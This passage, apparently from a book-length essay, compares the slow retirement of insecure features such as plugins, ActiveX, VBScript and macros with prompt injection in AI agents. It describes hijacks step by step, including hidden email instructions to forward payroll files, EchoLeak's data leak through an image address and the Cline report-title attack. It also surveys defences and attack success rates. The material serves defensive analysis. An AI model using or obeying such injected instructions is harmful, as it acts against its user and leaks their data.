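Mexican taxpayers faced a similar problem when Chrome dropped most plugins on Linux in 2014, well before it did so on Windows and Macs. In *Chrome for Linux planning to drop NPAPI support as soon as April*, a discussion on the Chromium developers' mailing list, a Mexican user wrote that his country's tax office relied on Java and Silverlight, and that about 40 million taxpayers could not pay their taxes without them. Another participant asked how many of them used Linux. The Mexican user himself thought that nearly all professional accountants used Windows and Internet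 Explorer, so the change must have affected far fewer than 40 million people. According to Google, fewer than 0.7 per cent of Chrome's Linux users had launched any given one of the affected plugins in a month.

The protester was still right that his problem was serious, because he had to file taxes and could not choose another tax office. Google could not repair the Mexican site, and the tax office had little reason to hurry while other browsers still ran the plugins. The protester said he was leaving Chrome. When a participant asked in 2015 whether Google had lost users over the change, a Google engineer doubted that the effect was measurable.

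### Ways of buying time

Vendors found several ways to delay or soften the breakage. The effect of these measures on security depended mostly on whether they had an end date and how many people they left exposed.

An override lets an administrator or user turn a blocked feature back on. Chrome's override for plugins expired after about five months, so companies could not postpone replacing them indefinitely. Office users can still re-enable ActiveX, and no end date has been announced. An override with no end date prolongs exposure, but only for those who change the setting, rather than for everyone, as leaving the feature on by default would.

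Long notice is easy for the vendor to give and lets honest customers adapt, but the feature keeps running in the meantime, as Flash did. SARS shows that customers may use the time badly if they don't believe in the deadline. When a vendor withdraws a change after complaints, as Microsoft did with macro blocking in July 2022, customers may learn to doubt the next one.

Paid extended support makes customers who delay upgrading bear some of the cost. Microsoft ended ordinary support for Windows 10 in October 2025 and offered businesses up to three more years of security updates, at $61 per computer for the first year and twice as much each following year. All three years cost $427 per computer, which gives companies a reason to upgrade sooner. The updates shorten the time that paying customers are exposed to newly found bugs, but they do not remove a dangerous feature that works as designed.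 The vendor also earns money from customers who stay on the old system.

A compatibility mode keeps old software available for selected uses. Microsoft retired the Internet Explorer program on most versions of Windows 10 in June 2022, but kept its engine inside Edge as Internet Explorer mode, which can still run ActiveX controls. Companies list the sites that need the mode, and Edge opens everything else with its modern engine. This reduces the exposure from the whole web to the listed sites, but it keeps the old engine on Windows. Microsoft has promised to support the mode until at least 2029 and to give a year's notice before ending it.

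Attackers got around the list by persuading people to reload a fake website in Internet Explorer mode, then exploiting an unpatched flaw in the old script engine. Microsoft learned of this in August 2025. It removed the toolbar button and menu entries that made switching easy, and home users now have to add each site in Edge's settings. Companies' own lists kept working as before.

### VBScript's slow retirement

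VBScript, a scripting language Microsoft introduced in 1996, shows how long it can take to retire a feature when the vendor tries to break as little as possible. It ran in web pages and directly on Windows. In May 2000 the ILOVEYOU worm, written in VBScript, spread around the world as an email attachment. Companies also used the language for routine administration, such as setting up computers when employees logged in.

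Microsoft restricted the two uses separately. In 2019 it disabled VBScript by default for internet sites in Internet Explorer, which few honest websites still needed. In October 2023 it announced that VBScript would eventually leave Windows altogether, and in May 2024 it set out three stages:

1. From the 2024 release of Windows 11, VBScript became an optional component, still installed and switched on by default.
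2. Around 2027 Microsoft would switch it off by default, and companies that needed it could turn it back on.
3. In a later release, for which Microsoft gave no date, it would remove the component completely.

On this timetable, VBScript is still on by default in late 2026, 26 years after ILOVEYOU. Many Office macros relied on it to search text, and their owners may not have known this until Microsoft warned them. In 2025 Microsoft built those functions into Office's own macro language so that these macros could keep working after VBScript is removed. Such changes reduce the number of customers that removal would harm, but finding them all takes years.

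### When removal itself does harm

Disabling an insecure feature can stop a tax form from opening or a payroll macro from running on payday, which harms people who did nothing wrong. Security engineers can underestimate this harm because they study attacks. Features that many people use for legitimate work often do more good than harm in any given year.

Removing a feature suddenly may also push people towards something worse. The protester in Mexico had first gone back from Chrome 35 to version 34, which still ran his plugins. A Google engineer warned that this was "very" dangerous because the old version would get no later security fixes, and that instructions for doing it were circulating. He advised using Firefox for the few pages that needed a plugin. Nobody in the discussion knew how many people had downgraded. Korea's banks had years to prepare for the loss of ActiveX and still worked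 around it, on a much larger scale, so more notice would not have been enough without a reason to give up installed software altogether.

Vendors have the best reason to delay removing an insecure feature when a substitute is on its way, as HTML5 was for Flash, because dependence may then shrink without a ban. They have the least reason while customers are still building on the feature, since each year adds systems that removal will break. Vendors could often have switched a feature off for new documents and sites while exempting existing ones for a limited time. Microsoft came close with ActiveX Opt-In in 2006, but its exemption for controls already in use had no end date.

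## Prompt injection in AI agents, 2022 to 2026

Companies have connected AI agents to mailboxes, browsers and files knowing that hidden text could hijack them, and they are still building on these agents. The programmer Simon Willison named this attack prompt injection in September 2022, before OpenAI released ChatGPT. At first it mostly made chatbots write silly things, but it became more dangerous once models could send mail, click buttons and run code.

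### An email that gives orders

Suppose the clerk who opened the malicious spreadsheet now has an agent that reads and sends her mail. She asks it to summarise her unread messages. One looks like a delivery notice, but its sender has hidden an instruction in white text on a white background to forward the latest payroll file to an outside address and leave this out of the summary.

1. The agent's program starts a prompt with the developer's instructions and adds the clerk's request.
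2. The model replies with a command to use the mail tool, and the program fetches the unread messages.
3. The program adds the messages to the same prompt. The white line goes in with the rest, because colour does not matter to a program that reads text.
4. The model continues the prompt. If the hidden line has more influence on it than the clerk's request, it writes a command to forward the payroll file.
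5. The program carries out that command through the clerk's account.

The mail server receives a valid request from someone allowed to send the file, and the clerk sees an ordinary summary. Nobody stole a password, and an engineer would find no coding error in the agent's program.

### One sequence of tokens

A language model receives its prompt as a sequence of tokens, which are words or pieces of words. It calculates how likely each possible token is to come next:

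P(next token | t₁, t₂, …, tₙ)

The program picks a token, adds it to the sequence and runs the model again. The developer may have written the first 200 tokens, the clerk the next 15 and a stranger some of the rest, but the model processes them all as the same kind of input. Developers put special markers where each part begins and train models to give the developer's instructions priority. But the markers are also tokens in the sequence, and they work only as well as the model has learned to respond to them.

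A database can work out the structure of a parameterised query before it processes the visitor's value, but a model has no such earlier stage. It has to read an email to summarise it, and anything it reads can affect what it writes next.

Honest emails often contain instructions, so deleting every instruction from incoming mail would not solve the problem. A supplier may write "please return the signed form by Friday", and the clerk may want her agent to do it. Whether the agent should act depends on who is asking and what the clerk wants, which the wording alone does not show.

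### "Inherently confusable"

In a December 2025 post for the NCSC, David C gives the technical argument that prompt injection cannot be fixed. He describes how developers join their own instructions to untrusted content, then treat the model's answer as if the two had been kept separate. His example is a recruitment system that scores CVs. A candidate hides a line in a CV telling the system to approve it for interview, and the system follows the line as an instruction.

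SQL injection, cross-site scripting (which plants an attacker's script in someone else's web page) and buffer overflows occur in systems that handle data and instructions differently, so engineers can enforce the separation. A language model only predicts the next token, and has no such built-in distinction. Developers can train it to prefer some text or label the rest as data, but these defences do not change how the underlying technology works.

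He therefore proposes treating the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". Engineers can fix an ordinary confused deputy, such as the ActiveX control that deleted any file a web page named, by making it check on whose behalf it is acting. He does not think this can be done reliably for a model, so he recommends planning for a hijacked agent and limiting what it could do. He suggests that a system that cannot tolerate the remaining risk may be a poor use for a language model.

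Two weeks later OpenAI said much the same about Atlas, its web browser with a ChatGPT agent that can click and type as the user would. In *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025), the company conceded that prompt injection is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'" and compared it to scams aimed at people. OpenAI had a commercial reason to sound more confident, which makes the concession more credible.

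The argument shows that a model cannot guarantee its own resistance, but not how often attacks must succeed. Banks still function even though the people who run them sometimes fall for scams. David C writes of a "good chance" that the problem will never be properly mitigated, which leaves room for a better architecture. Developers have worked on models so resistant that attackers would give up, and on designs in which a hijacked model could do little harm. Either would weaken his case in practice.

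### Training a model to resist

OpenAI trains a model to attack its Atlas agent using reinforcement learning, which rewards a model for success. The attacker proposes a malicious text, a simulator shows how the agent would respond, and the attacker revises the text and tries again. OpenAI then retrains the agent on the attacks that worked.

One of these attacks was an email planted in a user's inbox. When the user later asked the agent to draft an out-of-office reply, the agent came across the email and sent the user's chief executive a resignation letter instead. OpenAI says the attacker found methods that human testers had not and can steer an agent through harmful tasks of tens or even hundreds of steps.

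OpenAI's updated agent detected the planted email and alerted the user, according to BusinessGhana's *OpenAI says AI browsers may always be vulnerable to prompt injection attacks*. OpenAI declined to say whether the update had measurably reduced successful attacks. Nolan (2025), in *OpenAI says prompt injections that can trick AI browsers like ChatGPT Atlas*, reported that Charlie Eriksen of Aikido Security doubted that this kind of testing changes the underlying problem. Eriksen thought agents need clearer limits on what they may do and whose instructions they should follow.

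A later experiment suggests one way that such training goes wrong. Help Net Security's *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection* (2026) describes how researchers at the University of Waterloo, Zhejiang University and KTH in Stockholm tested two automated attack tools on Qwen3-4B, a small language model, in 560 practice tasks. One tool, PISmith, broke into 69 per cent of the tasks and produced 7,132 working attacks. The other, RL-Hammer, broke into 33 per cent and produced 4,282.

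The researchers retrained one copy of the model on each collection, then tried three attacks that neither copy had been trained on. At worst, attackers hijacked the copy trained on the larger collection in 19 of 40 tasks, and the other copy in 11 of 40. The smaller collection also gave the better defence in two of the three other set-ups. The sample was small, and the researchers had chosen those tasks because simple attacks already worked on them. The larger collection probably gave the weaker defence because its thousands of attacks taught the model to resist only a few methods. Once a tool found a trick, such as telling the agent that the user's task was already finished, it reused the trick in new words.

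An alternative method, PIPETTE, rewards the attacking tool for finding new techniques and trains the agent to check each action against the user's request. After this training, ready-made attacks succeeded less than 0.5 per cent of the time on average on AgentDojo, a public set of everyday agent tasks. Attackers who rewrote their text about 250 times still succeeded on up to 10 per cent of 40 difficult tasks. Without attacks, the hardened Qwen3-4B completed 65 per cent of its tasks, up from 62 per cent before training, so it had not become too cautious to work.

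### Filters and labels

A filter examines incoming text and removes what looks like an attack. Help Net Security reports that in one test on Qwen3-4B, a filter called PromptGuard blocked slightly more attacks than PIPETTE, but the agent using it finished only 16 per cent of its users' tasks. PromptGuard discards the whole email or document it flags, including the part the user asked about.

Filters also have to recognise attacks that can be worded in endless ways, so David C warns against blocking phrases such as "ignore previous instructions".

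Marking leaves the text in place and labels it as untrusted. Microsoft calls its version spotlighting. One variant replaces every space in an email with an unusual character to show the model which words came from outside. The developer instructs the model never to obey text marked this way. Microsoft's researchers reported in 2024 that spotlighting reduced the success rate of attacks from more than 50 per cent to below 2 per cent, with little effect on how well the model performed its tasks. However, the label does not prevent the model from obeying the marked text.

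These percentages depend heavily on the attacker, and researchers who designed attacks against a particular defence have defeated many published ones.

### Asking the user

Atlas asks for confirmation before some actions with serious consequences, such as completing a purchase or sending an email. A confirmation prompt would probably have stopped the resignation letter if the user had read the prompt. This defence requires no change to the model and works whatever wording the attacker used.

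Asking the user to approve actions takes up their attention, and an agent that asks about everything saves little work. Anthropic reported in 2026 that people using Claude Code, its programming agent, approved 93 per cent of permission requests. Most of those requests were presumably harmless, so the figure does not measure carelessness, but it shows how rarely people have a reason to refuse. Permission requests also cover only the actions the developer thought of. An agent can leak a secret by opening a web address that contains it, which looks like ordinary browsing.

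OpenAI advises users to give narrow instructions. A request to review all emails and take whatever action is needed gives hidden text more scope to misdirect the agent than a request to find one invoice.

### Limiting the agent with ordinary code

David C recommends safeguards that do not depend on a model's judgement. One rule he cites, from an online discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista, is that when a model processes someone's text, its privileges should drop to that person's. An outsider who emails a clerk cannot open her payroll files, so under this rule an agent that has read the email cannot open them either.

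CaMeL, a system that Debenedetti and colleagues at Google and ETH Zurich published in 2025, applies the same idea in detail. For example, the clerk might ask her agent to pay the invoice in a supplier's latest email.

1. A model that sees only her request writes a short program: find the email, extract the amount and account number, make the payment.
2. A separate model, which has no tools, reads the email and returns the two values.
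3. Ordinary code runs the program and keeps a record of where each value came from.
4. Before the payment, the code checks a policy, for example that money may go only to an account the company already has on file. If the account number came from the email and is not on file, the code stops and asks.

With CaMeL, an order hidden in an email to forward the payroll file has no effect, because the email's text never reaches the model that chooses the actions. CaMeL completed 77 per cent of tasks in AgentDojo, compared with 84 per cent for an unprotected agent. That is a small loss in exchange for a guarantee, but the guarantee covers only what the policies cover. Somebody has to write those policies, and a false amount in the email could still get through if no policy checked it. The method also works poorly for requests such as "do what this email asks", because the program cannot be written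 until a model has read the email.

Microsoft has a related system called FIDES, which labels data by how far the system may trust it.

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner et al., 2025) describes six simpler patterns that follow one principle: once an agent has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger an action with serious consequences. In one pattern, the agent can only choose from a fixed list of actions and never reads the results. In another, which would suit the recruitment system, a separate model scores each CV and returns only a number. A dishonest candidate might still raise their own score but could not change anyone else's or make the system send mail. Each pattern gives up some flexibility because Beurer-Kellner and colleagues doubt that general-purpose agents built on current language models can offer reliable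 guarantees.

### What developers reported in 2025 and 2026

Some developers publish attack success rates in system cards, the documents that accompany a new model and describe its tests. Anthropic's are the most detailed. VentureBeat compared Anthropic's card for Claude Opus 4.8 with OpenAI's card for GPT-5.5, which gave a single robustness score of 0.963, down from 0.998 for an earlier model. OpenAI's score measured resistance to known attacks in one setting, whereas Anthropic tested four settings against an attacker that adapted to the model's responses. Google and Meta gave no figure in their cards.

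Several of the Claude results come from Gray Swan, a security firm that runs its own tests. The Decoder reported them in *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* and *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. VentureBeat reported the results for Opus 4.6, which Anthropic released in February 2026, and Anthropic published the browser results for Opus 4.5.

| Claude model | Test | Attacks that succeeded | Source |
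|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.5 | Browser, with 100 attempts per environment | 8.0% for the model alone, 1.4% with new safeguards | Anthropic |
| Opus 4.5 | Gray Swan, very strong attacks | 4.7% after 1 attempt, 33.6% after 10, 63% after 100 | The Decoder |
| Opus 4.6 | Restricted coding environment, no safeguards | 0% in 200 attempts | VentureBeat |
| Opus 4.6 | Operating a computer through its screen | 17.8% after 1 attempt and 78.6% after 200 without safeguards, 57.1% after 200 with them | VentureBeat |
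| Opus 4.8 | 129 browser environments, before safeguards | 31.5% | VentureBeat |
| Opus 4.8 | Gray Swan, up to 15 attempts | 5.5% | The Decoder |
| Opus 5 | Gray Swan, up to 15 attempts | 2.0% | The Decoder |
| Opus 5 | 129 browser scenarios | 0% | The Decoder |

Resistance to prompt injection depends on the setting as much as the model. Opus 4.6 resisted every attack in the coding test, but attackers who kept trying usually succeeded when it operated a computer through its screen. Success rates also depend on the number of attempts, so a rate reported without that number means little. The attackers and environments may have differed between Anthropic's browser tests of Opus 4.5 and 4.8, so the apparent sharp decline in resistance may not be real.

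The zero for Opus 5, from July 2026, is the best browser result in the table. If the 129 scenarios were a random sample of hostile pages, a true rate of up to about 2.3 per cent would still produce no successful attacks at least one time in twenty. But the scenarios were chosen in advance, and real attackers look for cases nobody tested. Some of the improvement over Opus 4.8 may also come from the safeguards, if Anthropic had them on only for the Opus 5 figure.

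Opus 5.5 followed in September. According to Anthropic's *System Card* (2026), it performed similarly to or better than Opus 5 on every prompt injection test reported, without the extra safeguards Anthropic uses in its products, but it is more likely than earlier models to follow some malicious instructions. In October, Pogorelec (2026) reported progress in Claude Haiku 5.5, a cheaper model for quick, repetitive work, in *Anthropic's new budget model gets much better at ignoring hidden commands*. This may matter more than another gain in the top models, since cheap models are the natural choice for reading large amounts of mail. Anthropic released Claude Fable 5.2 and Mythos 5.2 in November, so the table does not describe its latest models.

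### One per cent, a hundred times

In late 2025 Anthropic put the success rate against its browser agent at about 1 per cent. PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots* described this as a meaningful risk rather than a solved problem. Suppose an agent meets 100 hostile emails or pages in a year, and each has a 1 per cent chance of hijacking it independently of the others. The chance that all of them fail is 0.99 multiplied by itself 100 times, or about 0.37. The chance of at least one hijack is therefore

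1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰ ≈ 0.63

or 63 per cent. At a rate of 0.1 per cent it would be about 10 per cent, and the agent would need to meet 1,000 hostile items to reach 63.

Real attempts are not independent. At 4.7 per cent per attempt, the formula gives Gray Swan's attacks on Opus 4.5 a 38 per cent chance of succeeding within 10 attempts and a 99 per cent chance within 100. The measured rates were 34 and 63 per cent (the 63 matches the worked example only by coincidence). Some targets evidently resisted however often the attacker tried.

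The dependence can also help the attacker. Agents that run on the same model have much the same weak points, so an attacker can experiment on a private copy until one text works, then send that text to thousands of people. The average attack success rate in a system card is a poor guide to their risk, because the attacker has already discarded the texts that fail.

### Demonstrations and real harm

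Most known attacks are demonstrations. When the Atlas browser appeared in October 2025, researchers and users showed within days that a few words in a Google Doc could redirect its agent. Fortune (2025) describes another attack, in which a button on a web page secretly copied the attacker's text to the clipboard. The browser company Brave had already found a flaw in Comet, Perplexity's browser. Constantin (2026) reports in *AI agent security* that four research teams broke AI agents in four different ways within ten days in July 2026. Their targets included Anthropic's Claude for Chrome extension and an agent's stored memory.

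In June 2025, the company Aim Security disclosed EchoLeak, a demonstration attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, which many businesses already used to answer employees' questions from company mail and files. The attack used an email from an outsider, written as if to a human reader so that Microsoft's filter would not flag it. When the employee later asked Copilot about a related subject, Copilot retrieved the email along with internal documents and followed the email's instructions. It put confidential text into the address of a picture in its answer, and the employee's browser requested the picture automatically. EFAIL had used a picture's address in the same way. The employee did not have to click anything, or even open the email. Microsoft gave the flaw a CVE number, rated it critical, fixed it on its own servers and said that no customers had been affected.

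Confirmed harm is much rarer. One case, in February 2026, involved Cline, a programming agent. Its developers used an AI system to sort the problem reports that anyone could post on their public page, and that system could run commands. The researcher Adnan Khan showed that instructions in a report's title could hijack the system and expose the passwords used to publish Cline. Days after he published this, someone released an altered version of Cline, apparently using the same method, that installed another AI agent on users' computers without their permission. About 4,000 people downloaded it before the developers withdrew it. The damage was small because the added program was not malware, but the attacker could as easily have installed a harmful one.

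Other people have used hidden instructions for minor advantages. In July 2025 the Japanese newspaper Nikkei found 17 research papers containing hidden requests for AI reviewers to praise them. Underhill (2026), in *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks*, reported in August that criminals were also developing tools to target agents.

The small number of known victims is weak evidence that there are few victims. A hijacked agent acts through its user's account, so its actions look like the user's, and the user may have no reason to check. David C recommends keeping records of what a model reads, writes and does with its tools. He adds that attackers usually need several tries, so a run of failed tool calls may be an early warning.

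### What agents do by default

Developers ship agents that can read untrusted content from the start, and mostly restrict what the agents do afterwards. When OpenAI described Atlas in December 2025, its agent could use websites the user had logged in to, but asked before making purchases or sending emails. On sensitive sites, a "watch mode" kept the user involved. Atlas also had a logged-out mode, in which the agent could not use the user's accounts. OpenAI recommended this mode for tasks that did not need those accounts, but users had to select it.

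When Anthropic's Chrome extension appeared in 2025, it asked for permission before publishing, buying or sharing personal data, and it could not be used on some kinds of site, including financial services. In December 2025 Google published a design for Chrome's agent that relies more on limits in ordinary code, which restrict the sites the agent may read from and act on during a task. A second model, which does not see the web pages, compares each proposed action with the user's request. Chrome also asks for permission before making purchases, sending messages or using saved passwords.

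Makers of email assistants have mainly responded by closing the routes through which data could leave. Google said in June 2025 that its Gemini assistant would not display images from external URLs in its answers in Gmail and its other office programs, which blocks the method EchoLeak used. Gemini still reads whatever arrives in the inbox, because its functions include summarising mail from strangers.

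## Do agents resemble retired plugins or permanent risks?

The older features suggest different futures for AI agents. Browser makers set an end date for Flash, C and C++ stayed in use with layers of protection around them, and AT&T defeated the blue box by moving its commands off the voice line. The table shows how many years passed between the first public demonstration and a default that protected ordinary users. Where no demonstration stands out, the count starts from an early attack or flaw.

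| Case | Why patches did not end it | Trust model | Years to a changed default | What forced the change | What followed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Telephone tones | No boundary between command and content | Any correct tone on the line | 15 (1961–1976) | Need for speed and capacity | Other toll fraud, later abuse of SS7 |
| SQL injection | Applications mixed the two, but a root fix existed | Filtering of input | No clear end (from 1998) | A decade of break-ins | Rare on websites, still frequent among reported flaws |
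| ActiveX | The feature was the danger | Signature and click | 10 on the web, 28 in Office | Phones and rival browsers, later security | Korean banks used ordinary programs instead |
| AutoRun on memory sticks | The feature was the danger | The device's own instruction file | Over 10 (to 2011) | Microsoft's infection counts | Worms used guessed passwords and a shortcut flaw |
| Java applets | Too many bugs | Sandbox | Over 16 (1996–2013) | Attacks, then browser makers | Exploit kits concentrated on Flash |
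| Flash | Too many bugs | Any page could run it | At least 9 (2007–2016) | Phones, HTML5 and a shared deadline | Fake virus warnings, stolen passwords |
| HTML email | Partly a missing boundary | Any sender's markup | 13 days in Enigmail (2018) | Publication of EFAIL | A related Thunderbird flaw in 2026 |
| Office macros | The feature was the danger | Click and signature, later place of origin | 4, reversed in 2007; then 27 (1995–2022) | Persistent macro malware | Disc images, shortcuts, OneNote, ClickFix |
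| C and C++ | The languages permit the bugs | Programmers' own checks | 31 for new Android code (1988–2019) | A fast, safe language | Attackers chained several flaws |
| AI agents | No boundary between command and content | The model's training and the user's approval | 4 so far (since 2022) | Nothing yet | Not yet known |

Hooked on Mnemonics' *Agentic AI Security* (2026) predicts that agents will repeat the history of computer security, but faster. The sequence may well repeat, but the intervals in the table depended on who controlled each feature and who relied on it, so we can't use them to predict when agents will reach each stage. The 2007 reversal on macros also shows that a quick change may not last.

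### Off by default, like a plugin

One position is that makers should switch off an agent's powers whenever it handles a stranger's text, as browsers came to do with Java. It needs three premises:

1. Makers can separate the dangerous feature from the rest of the product.
2. Users have another way to get the work done.
3. A few companies control whether the feature runs.

When Office blocks a macro, the user can still read the figures in the spreadsheet. An agent that cannot read mail cannot summarise it, so blocking all untrusted content would defeat its purpose. But makers can separate reading from acting. An agent without tools can read hostile mail, and the worst it can do is write a false summary. Makers should therefore switch off the combination of untrusted text and the power to send messages, make payments or run code.

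People often want an agent that can use their data and passwords to act for them. In *AI Injection Attacks* (2025), a post on the blog text/plain, Eric Lawrence, who works on Microsoft's Defender security software, gives the example of an agent that books a restaurant, orders flowers and emails a calendar reminder. An agent in a sandbox without the user's data and passwords could not do this. Lawrence expects a sandboxed agent to look much less attractive to people who don't know the risks of a powerful one.

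The premise about substitutes holds for single tasks. The clerk can send the payroll file herself in a minute or two, just as people could still open a memory stick's folder after AutoRun stopped. Sometimes a narrower program is enough. *LLMs' Data-Control Path Insecurity* (2024), an essay by Bruce Schneier on his site Schneier on Security, suggests that a traffic camera use a model that can only read number plates, since someone might hold up a sign that makes a general model ignore a plate. Nothing replaces a general agent the way HTML5 replaced Flash, because people buy agents for tasks that no developer foresaw.

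Few companies train the leading models or make the main browsers, so those companies could restrict agents, but they have less reason to than browser makers had with plugins. Browser makers gained little from Java applets, whereas Google, Microsoft and OpenAI sell the agents themselves. Lawrence compares their race to the build-up of nuclear missiles after the 1950s, with each company giving its agent more power for fear that a less cautious rival will win the market. The six companies that retired Flash agreed on an end date after its use had been falling for years. Agent makers would have to agree on one while demand is rising, and nobody could impose it on open-source agents.

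The comparison with plugins supports switching off particular powers that agents have, such as the ability to make payments after reading a stranger's email. It gives little reason to expect agents to disappear as Java applets did.

### Too useful to withdraw, like C

People who expect agents to stay can point to C and C++. In doing so, they assume that people depend on agents too heavily to give them up, that several imperfect defences together make attacks difficult, and that makers can gradually replace the dangerous parts.

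The evidence that people depend on agents is thin. TechRadar's *This popular AI agent could be hacked by a single email* cites a 2026 survey by the investment firm Menlo, in which 36 per cent of consumers had given agents access to their email, 33 per cent to web browsers and 20 per cent to financial accounts. These figures measure permission, which a user can withdraw in a minute, whereas Microsoft could not have removed C from Windows in a decade. If agents are going to become indispensable, restricting them is easier now than it will be later.

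Layers of defence work best when they fail for different reasons. Non-executable memory stops the processor from running data as code, whatever the attacker writes. But many of the layers around agents are themselves models that read the attacker's text. *Building Browser Agents* (2025) argues that stacking one vulnerable model on another gives no reliable boundary, and that even a 1 per cent failure rate is unacceptable for an agent with access to financial or communication platforms. Attackers can also develop one text that fools the model and another that fools its guard, then combine them.

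*Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) compares the problem to memory protection with a hypothetical no-execute setting that works only with some probability. The paper describes building a provable defence on such a foundation as challenging, and perhaps impossible.

An agent can also detect an attack too late. Manus, a general-purpose agent, could recognise hidden instructions in an email and warn its owner. But when researchers at Salt Labs disguised a small program in an unusual form of JavaScript, Manus ran it while trying to decode the message and gave the warning only afterwards. The program was harmless, and the flaw has since been fixed.

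*Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* is more optimistic about protective layers built from ordinary code. The 2026 paper compared four open-source agents and found that each used only some of the available protections, such as sandboxing and least privilege (giving a program only the permissions its task requires). Combining the protections the four already use would improve security without new research.

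The premise about gradual replacement applies least well to agents. In Android, old code became safer as people found its bugs, and new code in Rust could hardly add more of them. An agent has no comparable set of bugs to work through, because any text a stranger writes may be a new attack. Retraining can also make an agent more vulnerable, as it apparently did for some malicious instructions in Claude Opus 5.5.

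The closest equivalent to Rust is a design such as CaMeL, which stops nearly all the attacks in the AgentDojo tests, according to *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025). According to *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), CaMeL's loss of usefulness should shrink as models get better at planning and writing code. But even a better planner has to plan the steps before it reads the email. CaMeL does not yet do everything an unrestricted agent does, whereas Rust does nearly everything C++ does.

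### A separate channel, like the telephone network

Schneier starts from the blue box. AT&T could change its tones, complicate them or try to keep them secret, but it could not block the whole class of attack while commands and voices shared a line. CERT.at (2025), Austria's computer emergency team, makes the same comparison between language models and in-band signalling. The conclusion that only separation will cure prompt injection rests on three premises:

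1. Prompt injection works because commands and content share a channel.
2. While they share it, defenders can only stop attacks piecemeal.
3. Engineers can give the commands a channel of their own.

Schneier accepts the first two and rejects the third for current models. A language model is useful because the text it reads changes what it does, so he regards the mixing as a feature. He still expects a researcher to work out someday how to separate the two paths.

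AT&T spent a lot to separate its control signals from callers' voices, but callers lost nothing because an exchange never had to interpret what they said. An agent does have to interpret its email, and the more its actions need to depend on what the email says, the more usefulness it loses when the email is kept separate from its instructions.

Paying an invoice is an easy case, because the email supplies only two values. Christodorescu and colleagues give a harder one, in which a programmer asks an agent to summarise issue 7745 on a project's list of problems. The issue depends on another one, so the agent reads that too. The programmer is glad that the agent followed a direction it found in the content, because strict separation would have produced a poorer summary.

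Separating instructions from data fails completely for the open-ended requests that CaMeL handles badly, and for an agent that has to learn a new tool from its manual. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), by researchers from Google, NVIDIA, Gray Swan AI and several universities, notes that even defining this separation precisely remains an open question. It adds that false data could still get through. CaMeL has the same limit, which resembles the missing identity check in SS7.

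A reader of Schneier's essay objected that people trust human assistants, even though strangers can trick them too. Schneier answered that the kind of mistake matters as well as the number, and that people have millennia of experience with human mistakes. A clerk might be fooled by a convincing fake invoice, but she is unlikely to email the payroll to a stranger because of an instruction hidden in white text.

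The telephone comparison is therefore right about the cause, but its solution works only for tasks whose steps the user or developer can set in advance. For open-ended work, that solution removes much of the reason to use an agent.

### Windows 95, web pages and loaded code

Second Thoughts' *We're In the Windows 95 Era of AI Agent Security* compares agents with Windows 95, which let any program do anything to any file because it had to run software written for older systems. Microsoft and antivirus companies blocked one virus technique after another, but new ones kept appearing. Windows NT, a different operating system, fixed the problem, but moving everyone to it took until Windows XP became common in the 2000s.

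The article gives the best objection to its own comparison of agents with Windows 95. In 1995 engineers knew how to design a secure operating system, and Microsoft's difficulty was getting people to move to one. Nobody knows how to build a secure general-purpose agent, even in principle. Published designs so far either restrict what agents can do or make attacks harder without ruling them out. Agents are therefore a worse case than Windows 95, unless users will accept the restrictions.

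The article also warns against taking comfort in the small number of real attacks. Personal computers went on sale in the late 1970s, but viruses became a serious problem only 10 to 15 years later.

Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* compares agents with web pages. Since the 1990s, browsers have enforced the same-origin policy, which stops a script from one website from reading another site's data. An agent, however, can open every site its user is logged in to and carry text between them. Trail of Bits, a software security testing company, sent a hostile message to a test Instagram user. When the user asked the agent for a summary, the agent passed on contact names or parts of other messages. The company compares this attack to cross-site scripting. It compares other attacks to cross-site request forgery, in which a hostile page makes the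 browser send requests from the user's logged-in account.

The comparison is useful because web developers learned to contain both problems, partly by converting visitors' text so that browsers would display it and never run it. No equivalent conversion exists for an ordinary sentence that an agent reads. *Mind the Web*, a 2025 study, observes that browser protections against hostile scripts do not apply to its attacks, which use no script. An attack can consist of an instruction to click a button, placed inside a harmless-looking comment.

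Christodorescu and colleagues prefer a comparison with dynamic code loading, in which a running program fetches more code and executes it, as a browser does with plugins and scripts. They argue that some injected instructions are necessary, such as those in a tool's manual, so the problem is to limit what new instructions can do. Web browsers can identify the address each script came from and confine the script. Agents usually cannot determine where an instruction in the prompt came from, and have no dependable way to confine it inside the model. This comparison seems the most accurate because it explains why deleting every injected instruction would be a mistake.

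### Where agents differ from the older features

Makers of hosted models can update all their users at once. OpenAI released a newly trained model for its Atlas browser agent as a security update, according to The Decoder's *OpenAI admits prompt injection may never be fully solved*. By contrast, exploit kits were profitable because people had not installed the latest Java or Flash. This difference is a reason to keep agents and defend them in layers, although each update deals mainly with known attacks.

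It also covers only the model. The program around it often runs on the user's computer and ages like other software. Help Net Security's *Researchers broke the browsers built into VS Code, Cursor, Copilot, Codex* (2026) reports that the company Forever Security found weaknesses in five programming assistants. On 29 October, two of them, Codex and VS Code, still had no fix for a flaw that let one file in a hostile project read the rest of the disk.

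A malicious macro needed the user to click, but an injected instruction needs only an ordinary request that they would make anyway, such as asking for a summary of new mail. This favours restricted defaults, since training users to be suspicious does little when they never see the suspicious text. Browsers could protect careful users from drive-by downloads by requiring a click before Java ran, but agents already ask for approval, and people give it most of the time.

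A 2,600-hertz tone worked whenever it reached the right kind of trunk, but a text that has worked on an AI agent may fail on the next try. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) analyses a public competition in which 464 people made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models. An attack counted as successful only if the agent did the harmful thing and, in nearly all the scenarios, also hid it from the user in its final answer. When the researchers repeated successful attacks on the same models, many failed, though at least half worked again on the more resistant models.

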